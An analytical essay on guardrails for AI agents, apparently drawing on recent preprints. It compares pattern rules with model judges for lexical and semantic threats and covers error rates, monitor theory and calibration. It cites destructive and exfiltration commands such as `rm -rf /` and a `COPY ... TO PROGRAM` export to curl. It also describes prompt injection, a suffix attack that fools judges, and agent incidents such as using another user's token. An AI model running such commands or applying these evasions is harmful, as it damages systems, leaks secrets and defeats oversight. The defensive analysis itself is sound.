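# Do lexical and semantic threats to AI agents need different guardrails?

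## What agent guardrails check, and what lexical and semantic threats are

An AI agent is a language model that acts through tools. Unlike a chatbot that only writes text, an agent can run commands in a shell (a text interface for controlling a computer), fetch web pages, query a database or change the settings of a company's cloud account. To take each step, the model writes a tool call, which is a short structured request that names a tool and supplies its arguments, such as the command to run or the address to contact. A surrounding program called the harness, not the model itself, carries out the request and returns the result to the model, which then writes its next request.

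A guardrail is a check outside the agent that allows or blocks a tool call before it runs. The timing matters because many tool calls are irreversible. A developer can discard a bad sentence and have the model generate another, but, as Yang notes in *AgentTrust* (2026), retrying can't restore a deleted file or recall a secret already sent to a stranger.

AgentTrust, an open-source guardrail by one independent researcher, Chenglin Yang, is a fair example of the information a guardrail works with. For every tool call, it receives a record with seven fields: the type of action (such as a file deletion or a network request), the tool, a description in words, the parameters, the raw text of the command or query, a session identifier and the time. Yang's formal definition of the check also includes the history of earlier actions. Other guardrails get more or less information than this. In *guardscope*,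 Toyoda, Leung and U (2026) compared the positions a guardrail can occupy and concluded that its position determines which actions it can inspect and how much information it gets about them. A gateway in front of the harness sees the full content of every request that passes through it, but some actions bypass it. A monitor in the operating system's kernel registers nearly all of the agent's actions, but not their content.

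Guardrails can also screen text at other points. Microsoft's documentation for its Foundry platform lists four: when the user's prompt comes in, when the agent proposes a tool call, when the tool responds, and when the final answer goes out. A check on the proposed tool call can still stop the action.

### Verdicts and error rates

A guardrail returns a verdict on an agent's action, and AgentTrust has four possible verdicts. *Allow* lets the action run. *Warn* lets it run but shows the operator a caution. *Review* holds the action until a human or a stronger check has looked at it. *Block* refuses it. If the guardrail fails, for example because it cannot reach a model it relies on, AgentTrust defaults to *review*.

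Microsoft's open specification for agent controls has the same four verdicts under different names (allow, warn, deny, escalate). *Agentao* (2026), a harness with built-in permission checks, has only three (allow, prompt the user, deny). *SAFETY SENTRY* (2026) also uses three, and argues for separating "ask" from "refuse" because many earlier agent guardrails return only yes or no, which leaves the user to decide every case that a yes or no can't settle.

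Two error rates describe how well a guardrail does. The false-positive rate (FPR) is the share of harmless actions that it does not simply allow. The false-negative rate (FNR) is the share of dangerous actions that it lets run. With v for the verdict that the guardrail gave and v* for the correct one, Yang writes them as

FPR = Pr[v ≠ allow | v* = allow]

FNR = Pr[v ∈ {allow, warn} | v* = block]

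Under these definitions, a warning counts as a false positive on a harmless action and as a false negative on a dangerous one, since the dangerous action still runs. Neither rate includes actions that should get a warning, so mistakes on them affect only the overall accuracy. Neither rate means much without the other, because a guardrail that blocks everything has a false-negative rate of zero.

Published false-positive rates do not all use the same definition. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, an engineering article about permission checks in the company's coding agent, defines the rate as the share of harmless actions that the check blocks. This definition suits a check that only allows or blocks, but it makes the rate hard to compare with that of a four-verdict system. Suppose a guardrail handles 1,000 harmless actions, warns on 15, sends four to review and blocks one.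 Its false-positive rate is 2% under Yang's definition, which includes all 20 of those actions, but 0.1% if only the blocked action counts.

### The kinds of check

The simplest kind of check is a pattern rule, which tests the text of an action and is deterministic, meaning that the same input always produces the same verdict. It may be a blocklist of forbidden commands or a regular expression, a formula that describes a set of strings. The first version of AgentTrust includes 170 rules, one of which blocks `chmod 777`, a command that lets every user of the machine read and change a file.

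A context rule is just as deterministic, but it also uses trusted facts about the situation, such as who is asking, what the agent did earlier and where a piece of data came from. In an example from *ToolGuardian* (2026), an agent reads from a sensitive database and then updates a project on an external service. The agent is authorised to make each call, but a rule about their order denies the workflow because together they could let the data leave. *LEANGUARD* (2026) applies the same idea to agents that issue refunds or modify orders, where whether to allow an action can depend on the state of the company's records, a prior authorisation or whether the agent has already attempted the operation. AgentTrust has a session tracker that raises an alert when an agent reads a file of secrets, encodes it and posts it to the web, even though each step looks harmless on its own.

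The remaining mechanisms use a model. A classifier is a model trained to label inputs or actions as safe or unsafe. Meta's Llama Guard, for example, sorts chat messages by a fixed list of harms. A model judge is a general language model prompted to assess an action and return a verdict. Yang's judge rates five dimensions of risk, including data exposure and reversibility, then gives a verdict, a confidence between 0 and 1, and a sentence or two of reasoning. People use the two names loosely. For example, Anthropic calls its check in Claude Code a classifier, although it is a general model, Claude Sonnet 4.6, with a written prompt.

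### Lexical and semantic threats

The division of threats into lexical and semantic comes from Yang's second *AgentTrust* paper (2026), which appeared in June, a month after the first.

A lexical threat is a dangerous action that a check can recognise by a stable pattern in its text. The standard example is `rm -rf /`. On Linux and similar systems, `rm` deletes, `-r` extends the deletion to everything inside a directory, `-f` suppresses requests for confirmation, and `/` is the root directory, which contains every other directory on the machine. Practically no routine task calls for this command, so a rule can block it regardless of who issued it or why. The pattern needs to be written carefully, because programmers often use `rm -rf` on folders of downloaded packages, and an attacker can disguise the command, for instance by storing `rm` in a variable first. But if the pattern is good enough,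 more information about the situation would hardly ever change whether the command should be blocked.

A semantic threat has no such pattern. Its danger depends on the action's purpose, destination, content or scope. For example, an agent may use `curl`, a common command for sending web requests, to post anonymous usage figures (telemetry) to its own team's server. It may also use `curl` to send the folder that holds a user's Amazon cloud credentials to a thief's server. Yang treats the two requests as a twin pair, meaning a harmless and a harmful action that look the same, or nearly so, to the check.

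The two requests in this pair go to different addresses, so a list of approved addresses would be enough to distinguish them. Yang therefore adds a harder version, in which the agent sends the stolen secrets to a location the attacker controls on a storage service that the organisation has already approved. A rule that checks only the host would allow the theft.

According to Yang, the most realistic cause of such a theft is prompt injection, in which an attacker hides instructions in content the agent reads, such as a web page, a file or a tool's output, to redirect the agent from the user's task to the attacker's. The agent then makes the harmful call with the user's own permissions and tools, which is a large part of why the call looks ordinary.

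The definition of a semantic threat doesn't require an adversary, although the second AgentTrust paper assumes one who is free to make a harmful action look routine. Some of the best evidence that these threats can arise without an attacker comes from Anthropic's log of incidents involving its own agents. In one incident, an agent misread an instruction and deleted branches (parallel lines of work on the same code) from a remote repository. In another, an agent uploaded an engineer's GitHub access token to an internal computing cluster. In a third, an agent attempted migrations (changes to a database's structure) on a production (live) database.

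Anthropic describes a case much like the first in more detail, which shows how ordinary such an action can look. A user asked the agent to "clean up old branches". The agent listed the remote branches, built a pattern that matched some of them and issued a delete command. The user may have meant only the copies on their own machine. If they had meant the remote branches, the same command would have been right. The command was dangerous because of its scope. In the token case the problem was where the token was sent, and in the migrations case it was which database the agent chose.

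Anthropic attributes all three incidents to overeagerness, meaning that the agent took initiative in a way the user did not intend. It lists this as one of four reasons an agent might do something dangerous. The others are honest mistakes about how much an action will affect, a misaligned model that pursues its own goal, and prompt injection, which is the only one of the four that involves an attacker.

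Anthropic's system card for Claude Opus 4.6, a report on the model's testing and behaviour, describes more such incidents. Someone asked the model to open a pull request (a proposal to merge new code) on GitHub, but the model had no login there. It searched an internal system, found a misplaced access token and used it, although, according to Anthropic, it was aware that the token belonged to a different user. In another case, it destroyed changes that a user had already made in a repository. In one incident, the model had to set a variable whose name included `DO_NOT_USE_FOR_SOMETHING_ELSE_OR_YOU_WILL_BE_FIRED` to use an internal tool in an unsupported way. Most people would stop at that command, but a pattern rule would have stopped it only if the rule's author had anticipated that name or a similar one.

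Anthropic chose these anecdotes, so they show that harmless-looking dangerous actions occur without an attacker, but not how often. They also make "intent-dependent", Yang's other name for semantic threats, slightly misleading. Anthropic says the agents in its log were trying to help. Whether their actions were dangerous depended on what the user had authorised, whose token it was and which database was live.

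### Where the claim comes from

The observation that dangerous agent actions can look normal predates AgentTrust. *Structural Representations for Cross-Attack Generalization in AI Agent Threat Detection* (January 2026) contrasted traditional attacks, which exploit software flaws, with attacks on agents, which stay syntactically valid throughout and which a defender can detect only by understanding the behaviour around them.

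The same idea appeared in AgentTrust v1, in May, as a category of errors. Yang reviewed the nine scenarios out of 300 that the rules had misjudged. Four were commands under several layers of disguise, and three were typosquats, malicious packages whose names imitate popular ones. Yang filed the last two under "Semantic context required". The example is a `curl` command that uploads whatever another program feeds into it. The upload is harmless if the input is a build report and disastrous if it is a file of passwords, but the command line is the same either way. Yang described this as a limit of static analysis (analysis of a command without running it) and left such cases to an optional model judge.

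By June, Yang had made the difference between lexical and semantic threats the central claim of AgentTrust v2. Yang uses "rules" to mean regular expressions, matchers that work on the parsed structure of a command, and lists of permitted or forbidden items. Yang holds that a careful enough library of such rules resolves lexical threats with high precision, but that semantic threats are out of reach for rules "by construction". On this view, no pattern can catch a semantic attack without also catching its harmless twin, so writing more rules would not help. Yang supports the claim with an argument from these twin pairs and an experiment with extra hand-written rules.

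Telling the twins apart requires reasoning about what an action means, which Yang thinks a model judge can do and a deterministic matcher cannot. So v2 uses rules for lexical threats and a model judge for semantic ones.

All this rests on one preprint by one author, and the boundary shifts even within Yang's own work. In May, Yang treated typosquats as a problem of missing data, because the rules could not detect them without an external database of package names, and advised users to add one. In June, Yang placed a typosquat among the semantic twins, which supposedly no rule can catch, reasoning that the package's behaviour does not show in the install command. The June list of lexical threats also includes the creation of a cloud access key for a "foreign principal", meaning an identity from outside the organisation, but detecting this requires information beyond the command about which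 identities belong to the organisation.

Is the split between lexical and semantic threats a property of the threats, or of the information available to a particular check? An upload that can't be judged from the command line alone may need only a simple lookup if the check also has a record of where the data came from. The same goes for a migration if the check has a record of which database is in production. And if no pattern on the text can catch a threat, does a language model have to judge it, or would a fixed rule with better information be enough?

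## What a check can decide from what it sees

A guardrail takes some input about an action and returns a verdict, whether it uses a regular expression or a language model. For a pattern rule, the input may be only the text of the command, and for a model judge it is everything in the prompt. If two actions produce the same input, any deterministic check must give them the same verdict.

Suppose an agent issues the exact same command 100 times, and 10 of those uses are harmful. A deterministic check that sees only the command's text must either allow every use and miss the 10 harmful ones, or block every use and stop the 90 harmless ones. Deciding at random doesn't help. A check that blocks half the time will, on average, miss 5 harmful uses and stop 45 harmless ones, which makes 50 errors, compared with 10 for allowing every use.

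More generally, let p(x) be the probability that an action with input x is harmful. Allowing the action is a mistake with probability p(x), and blocking it is a mistake with probability 1 − p(x). The best possible check chooses the smaller of the two for every x, so the lowest achievable error rate is

minimum error = average over x of min(p(x), 1 − p(x))

In the example, p(x) is 0.1, so the minimum error is 10%. If every harmful action were matched by an identical and equally common harmless one, p(x) would be 0.5 and no check could do better than a coin toss.

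This formula counts a miss and a false alarm as equally bad, which they rarely are. Let M be the cost of a miss and F the cost of a false alarm. Allowing the action costs p(x)·M on average and blocking it costs (1 − p(x))·F, so blocking is cheaper when

p(x) > F / (F + M)

When p(x) is 0.1, blocking is worthwhile if a miss is more than nine times as bad as a false alarm. That is easy to believe when a miss means a stolen credential and a false alarm means a short delay. But if only one use in 10,000 is harmful, a miss has to be more than 9,999 times as bad.

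A guardrail can also send the action to a human. Suppose a false alarm has a loss of 1, a miss has a loss of 50 and a human review has a loss of 0.2. Allowing all 100 commands then gives a total loss of 500, blocking them gives 90, and reviewing them gives 20 if the human always decides correctly. The human can do that only with information the check lacks, such as whether they asked for the action. A reviewer who sees only the command has the same limit as the check.

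Extra input can lower the minimum error but never raise it, because a check can ignore it. Suppose the guardrail also records whether the agent opened a file of secrets earlier in the session. The agent did so before 15 of the 100 commands, and 9 of those 15 are harmful, compared with 1 of the other 85. The best check now blocks the 15 and allows the 85, which makes seven errors instead of ten. Some inputs leave the minimum unchanged. If the guardrail recorded the time of day instead, and 8 of 50 morning commands and 2 of 50 afternoon commands were harmful, the best check would still allow everything and make ten errors.

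### An information limit and an expressive limit

When Yang writes that rules can't separate semantic twins "by construction", the claim runs together two different limits.

When a harmless and a harmful action give a check the same input, no mechanism can tell them apart from that input alone. This is the information limit in the calculation above. Yang correctly says of two identical commands that "no function of that string can separate them", but this also applies to a language model that receives only the string, because the model is computing a function of it too. Sampling may add some randomness to the model's answer, but it doesn't add information about the action.

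An expressive limit applies when the inputs differ but no practical pattern captures the difference. It affects some rules and not others. In principle, a long enough list of exact commands could reproduce any set of verdicts on a finite set of inputs, but nobody can write that list in advance. A model judge may do better because its training included, say, dozens of ways to copy a database. But a judge can't learn from that training which storage account belongs to the user's company.

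Computer security researchers drew a similar distinction long before language-model agents existed. In *Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms* (2006), Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider separated two "often conflated" reasons why a mechanism might fail to enforce a policy. It may be unable to observe the events that matter, in which case replacing it won't help, or it may observe them but lack the computational power to use what it observes, in which case another mechanism might succeed. The second reason concerns what a machine can compute at all, whereas the difficulty with agent commands is more often what a person can feasibly write down.

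Yang's results suggest that the expressive limit accounts for much of the gap between rules and judges. The strongest judge tested, Claude Opus 4.8, gave the right verdict on at least 78% of actions in every category that Yang labels semantic. If every harmful action in those categories had an identical, equally common harmless counterpart, no check could have scored above 50%. So for most of the test cases, something in the judge's input must distinguish the harmful actions from the harmless ones. Yang's extra hand-written rules failed on some of these categories, but that doesn't show that no check could separate the two.

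### The five twin pairs

Yang illustrates semantic threats with five twin pairs. The pairs don't all run into the same limit, and for each one we can name a fact that would settle it or come close.

| Twin pair | Limit | Facts that would help |
|---|---|---|
| Telemetry or exfiltration | Neither, if the command names the address and the file; information, if the data arrives from another program | Which addresses belong to the team; where the data came from |
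| Ordinary upload or theft through an approved host | Information, if the check reads only the command | Who controls the storage location; where the data came from |
| Database read or bulk export | Expressive for a single export command; information for an export spread over many small reads | Whether the query sends data elsewhere; how much the session has already read |
| Reading a secret to debug or to steal | Information | What the user asked for; what the agent read beforehand; where the secret goes next |
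| Real or look-alike package | Expressive, if the name gives it away; information, if it doesn't | Who published the package; what its code does |

In the database pair, the harmless action is a query that returns at most 100 rows to answer a user's question. The harmful one uses the database command `COPY ... TO PROGRAM` to send the whole table of users to `curl`. The two texts are plainly different, so a rule could ban that phrase. Yang objects that an attacker could get the same data out in other ways, such as a variant called `\copy`, functions that run on the database server, or a loop that fetches the table page by page. Most of these are still visible in the text, so a check that understands database queries well enough could catch them. The loop is harder to catch because each of its queries can look exactly like the harmless one. A running count of the rows would help there, but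 reading each query more skillfully would not.

What a check can decide about the package pair also depends on the details. The harmful code is in a script that the npm package manager runs automatically after installation. A misspelt name is a clue that a judge could notice or a comparison with a list of popular names could reveal. But if an attacker takes over a genuine package, the install command stays the same, so a check has to inspect the package itself.

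The clearest case is `kubectl get secret`, which retrieves a stored password or key from Kubernetes, a system for running software across many machines. A thief and an engineer debugging a failed program can run exactly the same command. Yang also requires that AgentTrust never block a harmless action outright. To meet that requirement, a check that receives only this command must never block it, which leaves a warning or a human review.

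A guardrail can't look up purpose, so it has to infer it from the facts in the table. The user's request is probably the best evidence, but it is in ordinary language, and a fixed rule can't easily tell whether reading a particular secret is a sensible step towards "find out why the payment service keeps crashing". A model judge could, if it receives the request. A reason stated by the agent is weaker evidence, since a prompt injection can supply a false one. A program can keep or look up most of the other facts in the table, and a fixed rule can use them once another system supplies them.

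A guardrail can also avoid judging purpose. If the harm comes from sending the secret to an outsider, the guardrail can let the agent read the secret and restrict what the agent does afterwards.

### What a monitor can enforce over a sequence of actions

Restricting later actions in this way is an old idea with a well-developed theory. Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) studies monitors that watch a program step by step and stop it just before it breaks a policy. One example policy forbids sending any message after reading a file. The monitor needs only two states, "no file read yet" and "file read". The first read moves it to the second state, after which it refuses every send.

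Schneider proved that such monitors can enforce only safety properties. A policy is a safety property if every violation happens at a definite point and nothing afterward can repair it. Access control qualifies, because the violation is the forbidden operation. The policy "nobody waits forever for a resource" is not a safety property, because however long a wait has lasted, it might still end. Setting a maximum waiting time turns it into one, because the monitor can then act when the time runs out.

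Preventing information flow, the ultimate goal of an exfiltration check, is not a safety property either. Whether a message reveals a secret depends partly on what the message would have contained if the secret had been different, but a monitor observes only the run that happened. According to Schneider, monitors said to prevent information flow really enforce a stricter policy that also rules out some harmless runs. The ban on sending after reading is one such policy. It would stop an agent from posting stolen credentials, but also from uploading a build report it had read, which is the same tradeoff as blocking 90 harmless commands to stop 10 harmful ones.

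Ray's July 2026 preprint, *What Can Be Enforced?*, extends this theory to agents that call tools. Its example is an assistant that sends email and moves money under three policies. The assistant must never email personal information to a recipient who is not on an approved list, transfer more than a fixed total to any one recipient in a day, or send anything after the user revokes its access.

Ray requires a gate, the paper's term for a guardrail, to be sound and transparent. A sound gate never lets the executed actions violate the policy, and a transparent gate never blocks or changes anything in a sequence of actions that complies with the policy. Ray proves that a deterministic gate can be both if and only if the policy is a safety property and the gate has enough memory (states, stored values and counters) to recognise every sequence that is still acceptable. The transfer policy meets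 these conditions with a gate that keeps a total for each recipient and day and blocks any transfer that would take the total over the limit. For the revocation policy, the gate only needs to store one yes-or-no flag.

The email policy depends on whether a message contains personal information. Ray's theorem assumes that the gate receives correct answers to such questions from outside, and under that assumption a fixed rule can enforce the email policy as exactly as the other two policies. In practice, a fallible model supplies the answer, so the exact guarantee is lost. This boundary differs from Yang's because all three policies have simple rules, and the difficulty is getting the facts those rules need reliably.

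A gate can't enforce some policies even with perfect facts. Ray's example is a rule that a confirmation must eventually follow every payment. The gate has to decide on the payment before it is clear whether the confirmation will come. Some older monitors in the theory avoid this problem by holding the payment back and releasing it later, but a gate that must decide at once on an irreversible action can't.

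Ray also shows that the rules themselves can be hard to check. If a rule language allows two counters that can go down as well as up, no program can determine in every case whether a set of rules would ever block anything. Spending caps, rate limits and revocation rules fit in a narrower language, for which a program can always determine this.

### The trade-off between misses and false blocks

For policies that rest on a fallible judgement, Ray uses the Neyman–Pearson lemma, a 1933 result in statistics about the best test for a given error rate. Let β be the largest share of harmful actions that the guardrail may miss, and let I be the information it has. Ray defines roc_I(β) as the smallest share of harmless actions that a check using I can block while missing no more than β of the harmful ones. Plotting roc_I(β) for every β gives a curve, the frontier, and no rule, model or combination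 of models that uses the same information can get below it.

The best check ranks inputs by their likelihood ratio, which is how much more common an input is among harmful actions than among harmless ones. It blocks inputs from the top of the ranking until misses fall to β, deciding at random whether to block those at the cutoff if necessary.

If the check sees only the text, all 100 commands have the same likelihood ratio, so it can reduce misses only by blocking more commands at random. To miss only 5% of the harmful uses, it has to block 95% of the harmless ones. If the check can also use information about which commands followed the opening of a secrets file, it can block those 15 and a random half of the other 85. On average it then misses 5% of the harmful uses and blocks 53% of the harmless ones. The second figure is still high because the check can't distinguish the one remaining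 harmful command from 84 harmless ones.

Better information can't raise the frontier, but the frontier describes the best possible check. A particular model may ignore an extra fact or do worse with it. One of Ray's experiments separates what the best check could do from what a particular model does. It uses 123 tool calls from AgentDojo, a benchmark of prompt injection attacks on agents. Each call appears twice with identical text, once prompted by an instruction from the user, which Ray counts as authorised, and once by an instruction from a tool's output, which Ray counts as unauthorised. A judge that reads only the call must give both versions the same score.

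When the prompt included the source of the instruction, a 7-billion-parameter model rated the unauthorised version as riskier in 116 of the 123 pairs. A 3-billion-parameter model did so in only 15 and gave equal scores in the rest, and a half-billion-parameter model gave equal scores in every pair. All three models had the deciding fact, so the information limit no longer applied, but the two smaller ones mostly failed to use it. A one-line context rule that reads the source would get all 123 pairs right, because Ray defined the correct answer by the source. Real traffic is less clear-cut, for instance when a user asks an agent to follow the instructions in a document.

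### What calibration certifies

A judge that returns a risk score needs a threshold above which the guardrail blocks. Conformal calibration is a way to choose that threshold with a statistical guarantee. The developer collects n harmful actions, has the judge score them, and sorts the scores from lowest to highest. If δ is the acceptable probability of missing a harmful action, the threshold is the score at position (n + 1)·δ, rounded down. With 99 examples and a δ of 10%, this is the tenth-lowest score, so nine fall below it. For an episode of H actions, Ray divides δ by H, which keeps the expected share of episodes with any miss at or below δ.

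The guarantee covers only misses. If the position rounds down to zero, the method blocks everything, which meets the target but makes the agent useless. With a 5% target, the formula requires at least 19 harmful examples to avoid this for a single action, and at least 399 for an episode of 20 actions. However, Ray also describes a version that calibrates on whole episodes and doesn't divide by H.

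Ray tried the method with 23 judges on 97 harmless user requests and 35 attackers' goals from AgentDojo. These were written instructions, not tool calls, so the results give little evidence of how the judges would do on real actions, but they do show that meeting the guarantee can mean blocking many harmless requests. At a 5% target, every judge blocked everything. At 10%, Google's Gemma 2 9B missed about 1% of the attackers' goals and blocked 78% of the harmless requests.

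The guarantee also assumes that harmful actions in deployment are statistically like the examples, and an attacker has good reason to make them different. Ray added a short suffix to the attackers' goals stating that an administrator had already approved them. At a fixed threshold, the share of attacks missed rose by 20 to 60 percentage points for 8 of 11 judges, and the results for the other three were inconclusive. If such an attack can raise the miss rate by at most η per action, the bound for an episode of H actions rises from δ to δ + H·η, which soon becomes useless over a long episode. The transfer cap and the revocation rule don't depend on the text that the attacker changed, so the suffix doesn't affect them.

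### How blocking changes what the agent does next

The analysis so far assumes a fixed stream of actions, but an agent whose action fails usually tries something else. Ray proves that this can matter, using two systems that behave identically without a guardrail and on which the judge is equally accurate. After a block, one system stops safely and the other may propose a new harmful action. The second therefore needs more blocking to keep it safe, but no amount of data collected without the guardrail can distinguish the two. Yang's published error rates come from fixed lists of actions, so they can't reflect this effect.

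A gate that remembers what it has blocked can block fewer harmless proposals at the same level of risk. In a small model that Ray solves exactly, the agent makes a second proposal whenever the gate blocks its first. The second proposal always gets the same risk score, but it is harmful 60% of the time if the blocked proposal had a high score and only 2% of the time if that proposal had a low one, so the gate needs the history to tell the two cases apart. With the risk of an unsafe episode held to 5%, a gate with a memory blocks an average of 0.55 harmless proposals per episode, compared with 0.86 for a gate that uses only the current score and the step number.

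Ray also ran a small agent through 949 AgentDojo episodes under attack, with and without a gate. Without a gate, 45 attacks succeeded. When the gate used a 3-billion-parameter judge, only 4 did, but it blocked 78% of all tool calls, and the share of tasks the agent completed fell from 25% to 18%. A 7-billion-parameter judge with a higher threshold blocked 12% of calls and let 30 attacks through, a drop from 45 that could be due to chance.

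Ray reran the 389 episodes from the parts of the benchmark where attacks had sometimes worked, and compared each episode's outcome with and without the gate. With the smaller judge, 34 attacks succeeded only when the gate was off and 5 only when it was on. With the larger judge, 29 succeeded only when it was off and 22 only when it was on. Ray takes the attacks that succeeded only with the gate on as proof that blocking can push an agent into a different attack. That may well be right, but without a gate, 45 attacks succeeded on these episodes in the first run and 38 in the second, so some of the difference could be ordinary variation between runs.

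## Pattern rules on the text of an action

Pattern rules need the least computation of any check and usually use the least information. AgentTrust v1 relies on them for almost all of its verdicts. Yang tested that system with and without its main parts in May, then tested the same rules on unfamiliar actions in June, so there is a fairly detailed record of where the rules work and fail.

### One command through AgentTrust v1

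Suppose an agent is trying to fix a "permission denied" error on a website and proposes `chmod -R 777 /var/www`. The command would let every user of the machine change every file in the website's folder.

A component called the normalizer first checks whether the command is disguised. A shell accepts many spellings of the same command, because it fills in variables, translates character codes and drops some quotation marks before running it. The normalizer has nine strategies for undoing these disguises, all of which edit the text without running any part of the command. Later steps check the original and every rewritten version and keep the most severe result, so rewriting can't hide a danger. This `chmod` command isn't disguised, so it goes to the next step unchanged.

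Next, an analyzer checks the text against 42 regular expressions for risky file system, shell, network and credential features. A policy engine then applies the 170 rules. Each rule has a regular expression, the types of action it covers, a risk level and a verdict. For example, the rule for `chmod 777` has the risk level "high" and the verdict *block*. The engine uses the most severe verdict among the rules that match, and allows the action if none do.

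This means a new rule can make a verdict stricter but never more lenient. If an existing rule blocks something harmless, someone has to edit or delete that rule.

A session tracker also compares the agent's recent actions with seven attack chains, such as reading, encoding and sending a secret. It matches each step to a pattern and raises the risk level once enough steps have happened in the right order. It doesn't check whether the agent sent the same data it had read. Some chains resemble ordinary work. The chain for supply-chain attacks, which are attacks through software packages, consists of editing a project's list of packages, adding one and installing it. Programmers follow the same steps to add any package.

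The last step reports the verdict, the rules that matched, a confidence score and, where possible, a safer command. Here the suggestion is `chmod 755`, which lets only the owner change the files. The confidence score is a preset value, not an estimated probability. It is 0.95 when both a feature pattern and a rule match, 0.80 when only one does, and 0.60 when neither does. A chain alert raises it to 0.97.

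AgentTrust blocked this command, which matched Yang's label of *block*, but it rated the risk "high", one level below Yang's rating of "critical".

### Results on the first two test sets

Yang tested v1 on two sets of actions. The first has 300, with 50 in each of six categories such as file operations and credential exposure. The correct verdict is *allow* for 133 of them, *warn* for 38 and *block* for 129. The second set has 630 actions (188 *allow*, 98 *warn* and 344 *block*) and covers more cloud services, package managers and disguised commands. For comparison, Yang ran a simple blocklist of 50 patterns for well-known dangerous operations.

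| Check | Test set | Accuracy | False-positive rate | False-negative rate | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 50-pattern blocklist | 300 actions | 49.3% | 0.0% | 88.4% | 0.05 ms |
| AgentTrust v1 rules | 300 actions | 95.0% | 2.3% | 5.4% | 1.72 ms |
| 50-pattern blocklist | 630 actions | 37.9% | 0.0% | 85.2% | 0.03 ms |
| AgentTrust v1 rules | 630 actions | 95.4% | 2.1% | 6.4% | 2.04 ms |

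The blocklist's accuracy on the first set overstates how well it works. Of its 148 correct verdicts out of 300, 133 came from allowing every harmless action. It caught only 15 of the 129 dangerous ones. Yang included it as a lower bound, so its failure is weak evidence of how well a carefully written list of 50 patterns could do.

The number of patterns doesn't explain the gap between the two checks. An early version of AgentTrust with 22 rules scored 44.3% on the 300 actions, and the next version, with 68 rules, scored 94.0%. So 68 rules did almost twice as well as the blocklist's 50. A likelier explanation is that Yang developed AgentTrust's rules with this test set, and could see which actions the earlier versions got wrong. After that, more rules hardly helped. A version with 86 rules scored 97.7%, and one with 170 rules and the normalizer scored 97.0%, or two fewer correct verdicts.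 (The 97.0% includes four extra rules for made-up domain names such as `evil.com`, which Yang leaves out of the version meant for real use. Without them, the score is the 95.0% in the table.)

The labels also suit pattern rules. Yang assigned them using a written rubric. It raises the risk level of any action that touches a file matching a list of credential patterns, such as `.env` or `.aws/credentials`, and requires a *block* if the action sends the credential outside. A regular expression can apply much of that rubric, so high accuracy on this set is partly a result of the rules and the labels using the same criteria.

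The 630 actions were supposed to be a more independent test. Yang wrote them after freezing a version of the rules, but when an action revealed a missing rule, Yang added the rule and kept the action in the test. Yang discloses this in the first paper and doesn't claim there that the set measures performance on unseen cases. In the second paper, Yang describes the set as "not seen while authoring rules" but later acknowledges the added rules.

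Yang also switched off parts of the system one at a time. Removing the normalizer did not change the results on the 300 actions, few of which are disguised. On the 630, it raised the false-negative rate from 6.4% to 15.7%, or from 22 missed dangerous actions to 54. Since the rules stayed the same, this is good evidence that a rule's performance depends heavily on the form of the text it receives.

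Switching off the session tracker didn't change accuracy on either set, because every test case is a single action and the test program cleared the history between cases. Yang calls this a gap in the tests and proposes a new set of about 50 attack chains. That set would also need ordinary work sessions to measure how often the tracker raises a false alarm when someone installs a package. Switching off the tracker cut the median time on the 300 actions from 1.77 to 0.22 milliseconds, so the tracker accounts for most of the "2 milliseconds" that AgentTrust takes.

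### The external test set

For AgentTrust v2, Yang introduced a third set, with 189 actions in eight categories. Yang checked it for overlap with v1's material, and a second annotator, who was not an author of the paper, labelled all the actions again without seeing the original labels. The two sets of labels had a Cohen's kappa of 0.82. Kappa measures agreement beyond what chance would produce:

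κ = (p_o − p_e) / (1 − p_e)

Here p_o is the share of actions on which the annotators agree, and p_e is the share on which they would agree by chance. For these labels p_e is probably around 0.36, so a kappa of 0.82 would mean they agreed on about 88% of the actions.

On this set, the accuracy of v1's rules fell to 48.1%. The false-positive rate was 22.4%, about ten times as high as on the 630 actions, and the false-negative rate was 52.9%. Yang gives only percentages, but they are consistent with 13 false alarms on 58 harmless actions and 46 misses on 87 dangerous ones. The other 44 actions must have had a different correct verdict, presumably *warn* in most cases. If those counts are right, blocking every action would have been 46% accurate.

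Accuracy here counts only an exact verdict as correct, so some of the errors are mild. Of the 98 wrong verdicts, 39 were neither false alarms nor misses by Yang's definitions, including cases such as blocking an action that deserved a warning. The 46 misses are more serious, and they show that the rules did badly on unfamiliar actions.

Yang used separate development data to write more rules for cloud services, Kubernetes and continuous integration (automated systems that test and release software), then ran the old and new rules together on the 189 actions. Accuracy rose to 56.1% and the false-negative rate fell to 33.3%, while the false-positive rate stayed at 22.4%.

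The following table gives the accuracy in each category, alongside that of the strongest model judge, Claude Opus 4.8. The labels in the second column are Yang's. The number of actions is inferred from the rounded percentages and the overall scores, because only one set of category sizes appears to fit them all.

| Category | Yang's label | Actions (inferred) | Rules | Rules and added pack | Model judge |
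|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| `shell_persistence` | lexical | 22 | 73% | 77% | 82% |
| `fs_config` (file system and configuration) | mixed | 24 | 50% | 58% | 79% |
| `network_egress` (outgoing traffic) | semantic | 23 | 52% | 65% | 83% |
| `cloud_iam_secrets` (cloud identities and secrets) | mixed | 20 | 40% | 70% | 100% |
| `cicd_iac` (automated builds and infrastructure) | semantic | 25 | 36% | 48% | 96% |
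| `supply_chain_pkg` (software packages) | semantic | 20 | 50% | 50% | 80% |
| `observability_benign_hard` (monitoring) | semantic | 27 | 59% | 59% | 78% |
| `data_db` (databases) | semantic | 28 | 29% | 29% | 86% |
| Overall | | 189 | 48% | 56% | 85% |

### Does the experiment reveal a structural limit?

Yang considers this the paper's central result. The added pack was a serious attempt to help the rules, but it did not improve results at all in the packages, monitoring and databases categories. Yang concludes that the limit is structural, as the argument from twin pairs predicts.

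Yang's table labels five categories semantic, but rules improved two of them. Outgoing traffic gained 13 percentage points and automated builds gained 12, compared with 4 for the only category labelled lexical. Yang's text contradicts the table by putting these two semantic categories among those "with stable signatures". A later experiment uses a third grouping. Its "semantic slice" of 98 actions seems to include cloud identities, labelled mixed in the table, and to leave out automated builds and packages, both labelled semantic. If a category can count as lexical once rules have improved it, the claim that rules never improve semantic categories is hard to test.

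Small samples are part of the reason three categories showed no gain, but not the main reason. In the database category, the rules got 8 of 28 verdicts right, which gives a 95% interval of about 15% to 47%, so their true accuracy there is quite uncertain. The lack of improvement is less uncertain. Based on the inferred category sizes, the original rules made 57 errors in the five categories that improved, and the pack brought a net gain of 15 correct verdicts. At that rate, it should have gained about 11 more from the 41 errors in the other three categories. It gained none, which is very unlikely to be chance.

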